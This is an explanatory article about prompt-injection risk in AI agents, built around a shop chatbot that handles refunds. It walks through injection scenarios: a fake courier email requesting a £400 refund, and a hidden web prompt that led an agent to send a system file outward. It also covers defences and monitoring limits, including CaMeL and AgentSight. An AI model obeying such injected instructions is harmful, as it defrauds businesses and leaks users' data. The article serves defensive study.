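Suppose an attacker buys a £400 camera from the shop and keeps it. The attacker then poses as a courier and emails the support address about another customer's parcel, including an instruction for the model to refund the camera. When that customer asks about the parcel, the chatbot retrieves the email, and the model writes a refund request for the attacker's order.

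If the chatbot can only read the current customer's orders, the request fails because the application has no refund function. The attacker can still distort the reply, for instance by adding a link to a fake payment page, but can't get money directly from the shop.

If the chatbot can refund any order, the application sends £400 to the attacker's card. Even if the shop used GPT-6 Astra, the attacker could expect a refund for every few hundred such emails the chatbot reads, and emails cost almost nothing to send.

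A third version can issue refunds, but only through a function like this one:

```
def refund(order_number):
    order = find_order(order_number, session.customer_id)
    if order is None or order.refunded:
        return "refused"
    if order.price > 50:
        return ask_staff(order)
    pay_back(order)
```

The model supplies only the order number. The application takes the customer's identity from the login session, so it looks for the camera among the other customer's orders and finds nothing. The injection succeeds against the model in all three cases, but the results differ:

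| What the chatbot can do | Result of the false courier's email | Result of a dishonest customer's message |
|---|---|---|
| Read the current customer's orders | A misleading reply | No access to money or other people's orders |
| Refund any order | £400 for the attacker | A refund of any order, at any price |
| Refund the current customer's orders, with approval above £50 | At worst, an unearned refund for the real customer | An unearned refund of up to £50 per order |

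The Frontier Model Forum makes the same comparison in its June 2026 advice. An injection that does little harm when an agent is isolated and has narrow permissions could expose data or change systems when the agent has broad access to files and stored passwords.

### Misuse of a permitted action

The third chatbot can still lose the shop money. A customer who has received a £40 lamp can claim that it never arrived and persuade the model to refund it. The order belongs to the customer, the price is below the limit, and the shop hasn't refunded it before, so every permission check passes. None of these checks can establish whether the customer deserves the refund.

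Williams described a similar problem in ordinary software in a 2025 interview with Pandagle. Attackers use a coupon several times or exceed a transaction limit, and "technically, the application is working as coded". He said there were "no perfect automated defenses" against this. His concession applies at least as strongly to agents, though he wasn't discussing them, because a model may make judgements that a fixed rule or an employee used to make.

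The shop can move more of the decision into code. It might allow an automatic refund only when the courier's tracking shows no delivery, and limit how many refunds a customer can receive in a year. These rules also turn away some honest customers, such as one whose parcel was stolen from the doorstep.

Williams also recommends approval by staff, but the Frontier Model Forum warns that people may click through requests without reading them, which creates only an illusion of oversight. An employee who sees hundreds of refund requests a day, nearly all of them legitimate, could easily do this. If the model writes the explanation that staff read before approving a refund, an injection can shape that explanation as well as the request. It would be safer for ordinary code to fill the approval screen from the order record and the courier's data.

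### The cost of tight limits

Williams doesn't claim that a list of permitted actions solves the problem. He told Smith that "we don't know in advance exactly what capabilities a robot needs" for a given goal, and that too many restrictions would remove the creativity that makes an agent useful. He called this a "runtime control problem" and said nobody had solved it yet.

The shop would face this problem when someone tried to return a gift. The recipient is entitled to help, but the third chatbot can't look up the order because it belongs to the buyer. The developer could give the chatbot access to gift orders, but would then have to decide how recipients prove that a gift is theirs. Each unforeseen case requires a similar decision.

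In its brief, the Frontier Model Forum describes a partial solution, which is to grant a permission only when a task needs it and revoke it immediately afterwards. The shop could enable the refund function for one order after the customer presses a "request a refund" button on that order's page. The request comes from the customer's browser, so an attacker can't imitate it with text in an email. The forum notes that this works less well for recurring tasks, such as updating a calendar from an inbox every day, because the agent needs the permission again each time.

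The brief also discusses what Willison calls the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally. An agent with all three can leak data to an attacker, so one proposal is to forbid the combination. The shop's chatbot has all three, since it reads orders and emails and can put links and images in its replies. It would be safer if it never read emails, but then it couldn't tell a customer what the courier had written.

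The forum, whose members build models, trusts the model more than Williams does. It agrees that some limits should be in ordinary code, where no text can override them. But it also recommends training models to resist attacks and using classifiers to detect injections, because fixed limits alone may not balance security and usefulness well.

A company that relies on the harness also has to protect it. Smith calls it a new attack surface, and the forum's brief describes two ways to attack it. An attacker can plant false information in an agent's memory, where it may influence decisions long after the original email is gone. An attacker can also compromise a tool, whose results go straight into the model's input. The shop's refund function takes the customer's identity from the login session, which protects it from a poisoned memory but not from an attacker who can change the function itself.

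### A design that separates commands from data

In March 2025, Debenedetti and colleagues proposed a stricter design called CaMeL in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*. As the Frontier Model Forum describes it, CaMeL turns the user's request into a program in a restricted language resembling Python. A special interpreter then runs the program, recording where each piece of data came from and enforcing security rules.

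Suppose a customer asks the shop to cancel an order if the courier's latest email gives a delivery date after Friday. In simplified form, the system might write this program before any model reads the email:

```
email = latest_courier_email(order)
date = extract_date(email)
if date > friday:
    cancel(order)
```

A model with no access to tools can carry out the second step, which requires reading free text. If the email contains an instruction to refund a camera, nothing happens, because the program has no refund step and the email can't add one. The interpreter also records that the date came from an email, so a rule could prevent the date from affecting more sensitive actions.

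This is close to a parameterised query, because the system fixes the structure of the command before the untrusted data arrives. It also has the same limitation, since an attacker can still choose the value. Someone posing as the courier can get the order cancelled without injecting any instruction, just by writing that the parcel will arrive in three weeks. A dishonest customer can influence the program itself, because the system turns the customer's message into code. The shop would still need rules about which orders a customer may cancel or refund.

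The design has more trouble with tasks whose steps depend on what the agent reads. A customer might ask the chatbot to do whatever the courier's email says is needed to release a parcel. No program written beforehand can contain those steps, and taking them from the email would let its sender give commands again. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (2026), a survey of 41 defences, found that most can't support such tasks. A person could approve each step, but the agent would no longer work on its own.

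Counting blocked attacks is not enough to judge a defence, because an agent that did nothing would block them all. *AutoDojo* (2026), a benchmark that covers CaMeL and nine other defences, also measures how often an agent completes its task when nobody is attacking.

CaMeL is also slow. In the tests reported in *AttriGuard* (2026), it took roughly ten to a hundred times as long as an agent with no defence. AttriGuard, the rival defence that the paper proposes, took 32 to 41 seconds, about three times as long as no defence. These figures imply that CaMeL needed roughly two to twenty minutes per task, far too long for a customer in a chat window. The researchers had an interest in a comparison that favoured AttriGuard, and they used older models, but even a much smaller delay would matter to the shop.

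The security company Sophos wrote in *Inside the lethal trifecta* that no mainstream agent harness had adopted CaMeL. Sophos considers the design promising but advises companies to put simpler controls outside the model in the meantime. The shop's refund function, described above, is one such control and adds almost no delay.

### What sensors observe that logs miss

Since limits can't prevent every misuse, Williams also wants companies to watch their applications as they run. An application's log normally contains only what its developer decided to record. After a suspicious refund, the shop's log might contain one line with the time, the order number and the amount, but not the reason the application paid.

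A sensor inside the application can record much more at the moment of the refund, including the web request that started the process, the functions that ran and the database account they used. Williams told Pandagle that Contrast's sensors collect this kind of information and show an application's authorisation checks, which he said are often hard to work out from source code. In the shop, they might show that one path to the refund function never checks who the customer is. A developer could also log all this, but would have to anticipate the need.

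A sensor can trace an untrusted email through ordinary code, but the model's reply is newly generated text, and there is no precise way to tell which parts of it the email influenced. To be safe, a tool could correctly mark every reply as untrusted, but that mark wouldn't distinguish legitimate refunds from fraudulent ones.

Sensors inside an application can also miss what happens outside it. For example, a programming agent may run a command that starts a separate program, which those sensors can't observe. *Log Analysis for LLM-Based Agents* (2026) distinguishes instrumentation built into an agent's software from observation at its boundaries, such as its connections to tools and the operating system. Built-in instrumentation gives more detail about the agent's internal steps, while observation at the boundaries covers more of their effects. Sensors inside the application may be enough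 for the shop's chatbot, which has a few fixed tools, but a programming agent that can run any command also needs observation from outside.

Observing an attack doesn't stop it unless something responds in time. *AI Runtime Infrastructure* (2026) criticises agent monitoring tools for collecting data for people to inspect afterwards without changing what the agent does. Contrast also sells software that blocks attacks as they happen. But to block a fraudulent refund, the software needs a rule that distinguishes it from a legitimate one, which is the difficulty the shop had with the lamp.

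### The evidence for runtime protection

In Techstrong TV's *AI Can Find Every Vulnerability — So Why Can't We Fix Them?* (April 2026), Williams called it "crazy" that people don't use such runtime protection, "whether it's an AI app or a regular app or API", and said that it dramatically lowers risk. Part of his argument is that companies need something to stop attacks while they fix vulnerabilities. By his figures, an average application has 25 to 30 vulnerabilities and an average repair takes six months. He gave no source for those numbers.

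The argument for watching what the application does is stronger for SQL injection than for prompt injection. A sensor at the database can detect that an attacker's text has changed a command's structure, and can block the command until a programmer fixes the code with a parameterised query. Prompt injection has no comparable permanent fix, and the action it causes may look entirely normal.

Independent researchers have tested one form of runtime monitoring on an agent. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) describes a tool that monitors the agent from outside the application. The tool reads messages between the agent and the model, and records the programs the agent starts, the files it opens and the network connections it makes. The tool links a model's reply to an action when the action follows within a fraction of a second, or when the same file name, address or command appears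 in both. A second model then examines the linked record for suspicious behaviour.

The researchers asked a programming agent to download and build a project. The project's instructions led to a web page where a hidden prompt made the agent send a system file listing user accounts to an outside server. Zheng and colleagues' tool recorded the whole chain and reduced 521 events to 37, and the second model reported a probable attack. Across three programming tasks, the tool slowed the agent by an average of 2.9%.

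This shows that monitoring can connect an injection to its consequences with little slowdown. But the researchers tested only one attack, which they staged themselves, so the test can't establish how many attacks the tool would miss or how often it would raise a false alarm. The record also included the file leaving the machine, so in this test the tool showed how the theft happened but didn't prevent it. The second model reads text that an attacker may have written, so it is another possible target for prompt injection.

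Real attacks may be harder to spot than one that sends a system file to a stranger. The analyst firm Forrester warns in *Harness Up For Our Black Hat 2026 Recap* that an agent can do harm through a series of steps, none of which looks malicious alone. Forrester considers detecting harmful behaviour harder than recording actions, and understanding what an agent was trying to accomplish harder still.

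The evidence for sensors inside ordinary applications is older, but some of it comes from the companies that sell them. *Collaborative Application Security Testing for DevSecOps* (2022), an academic review, draws on presentations by the tools' makers when it reports that they can identify real vulnerabilities while an application runs. Williams told Pandagle that Contrast's false positive rate is below 1%, because the product reports only vulnerabilities it has observed in running code. That is the company's own figure for vulnerability reports in general, and it doesn't measure how many flaws the product misses or how well it detects prompt injection. A company considering the product for an AI agent should therefore ask what share of attacks it stops before they do harm and what share of legitimate actions it blocks.
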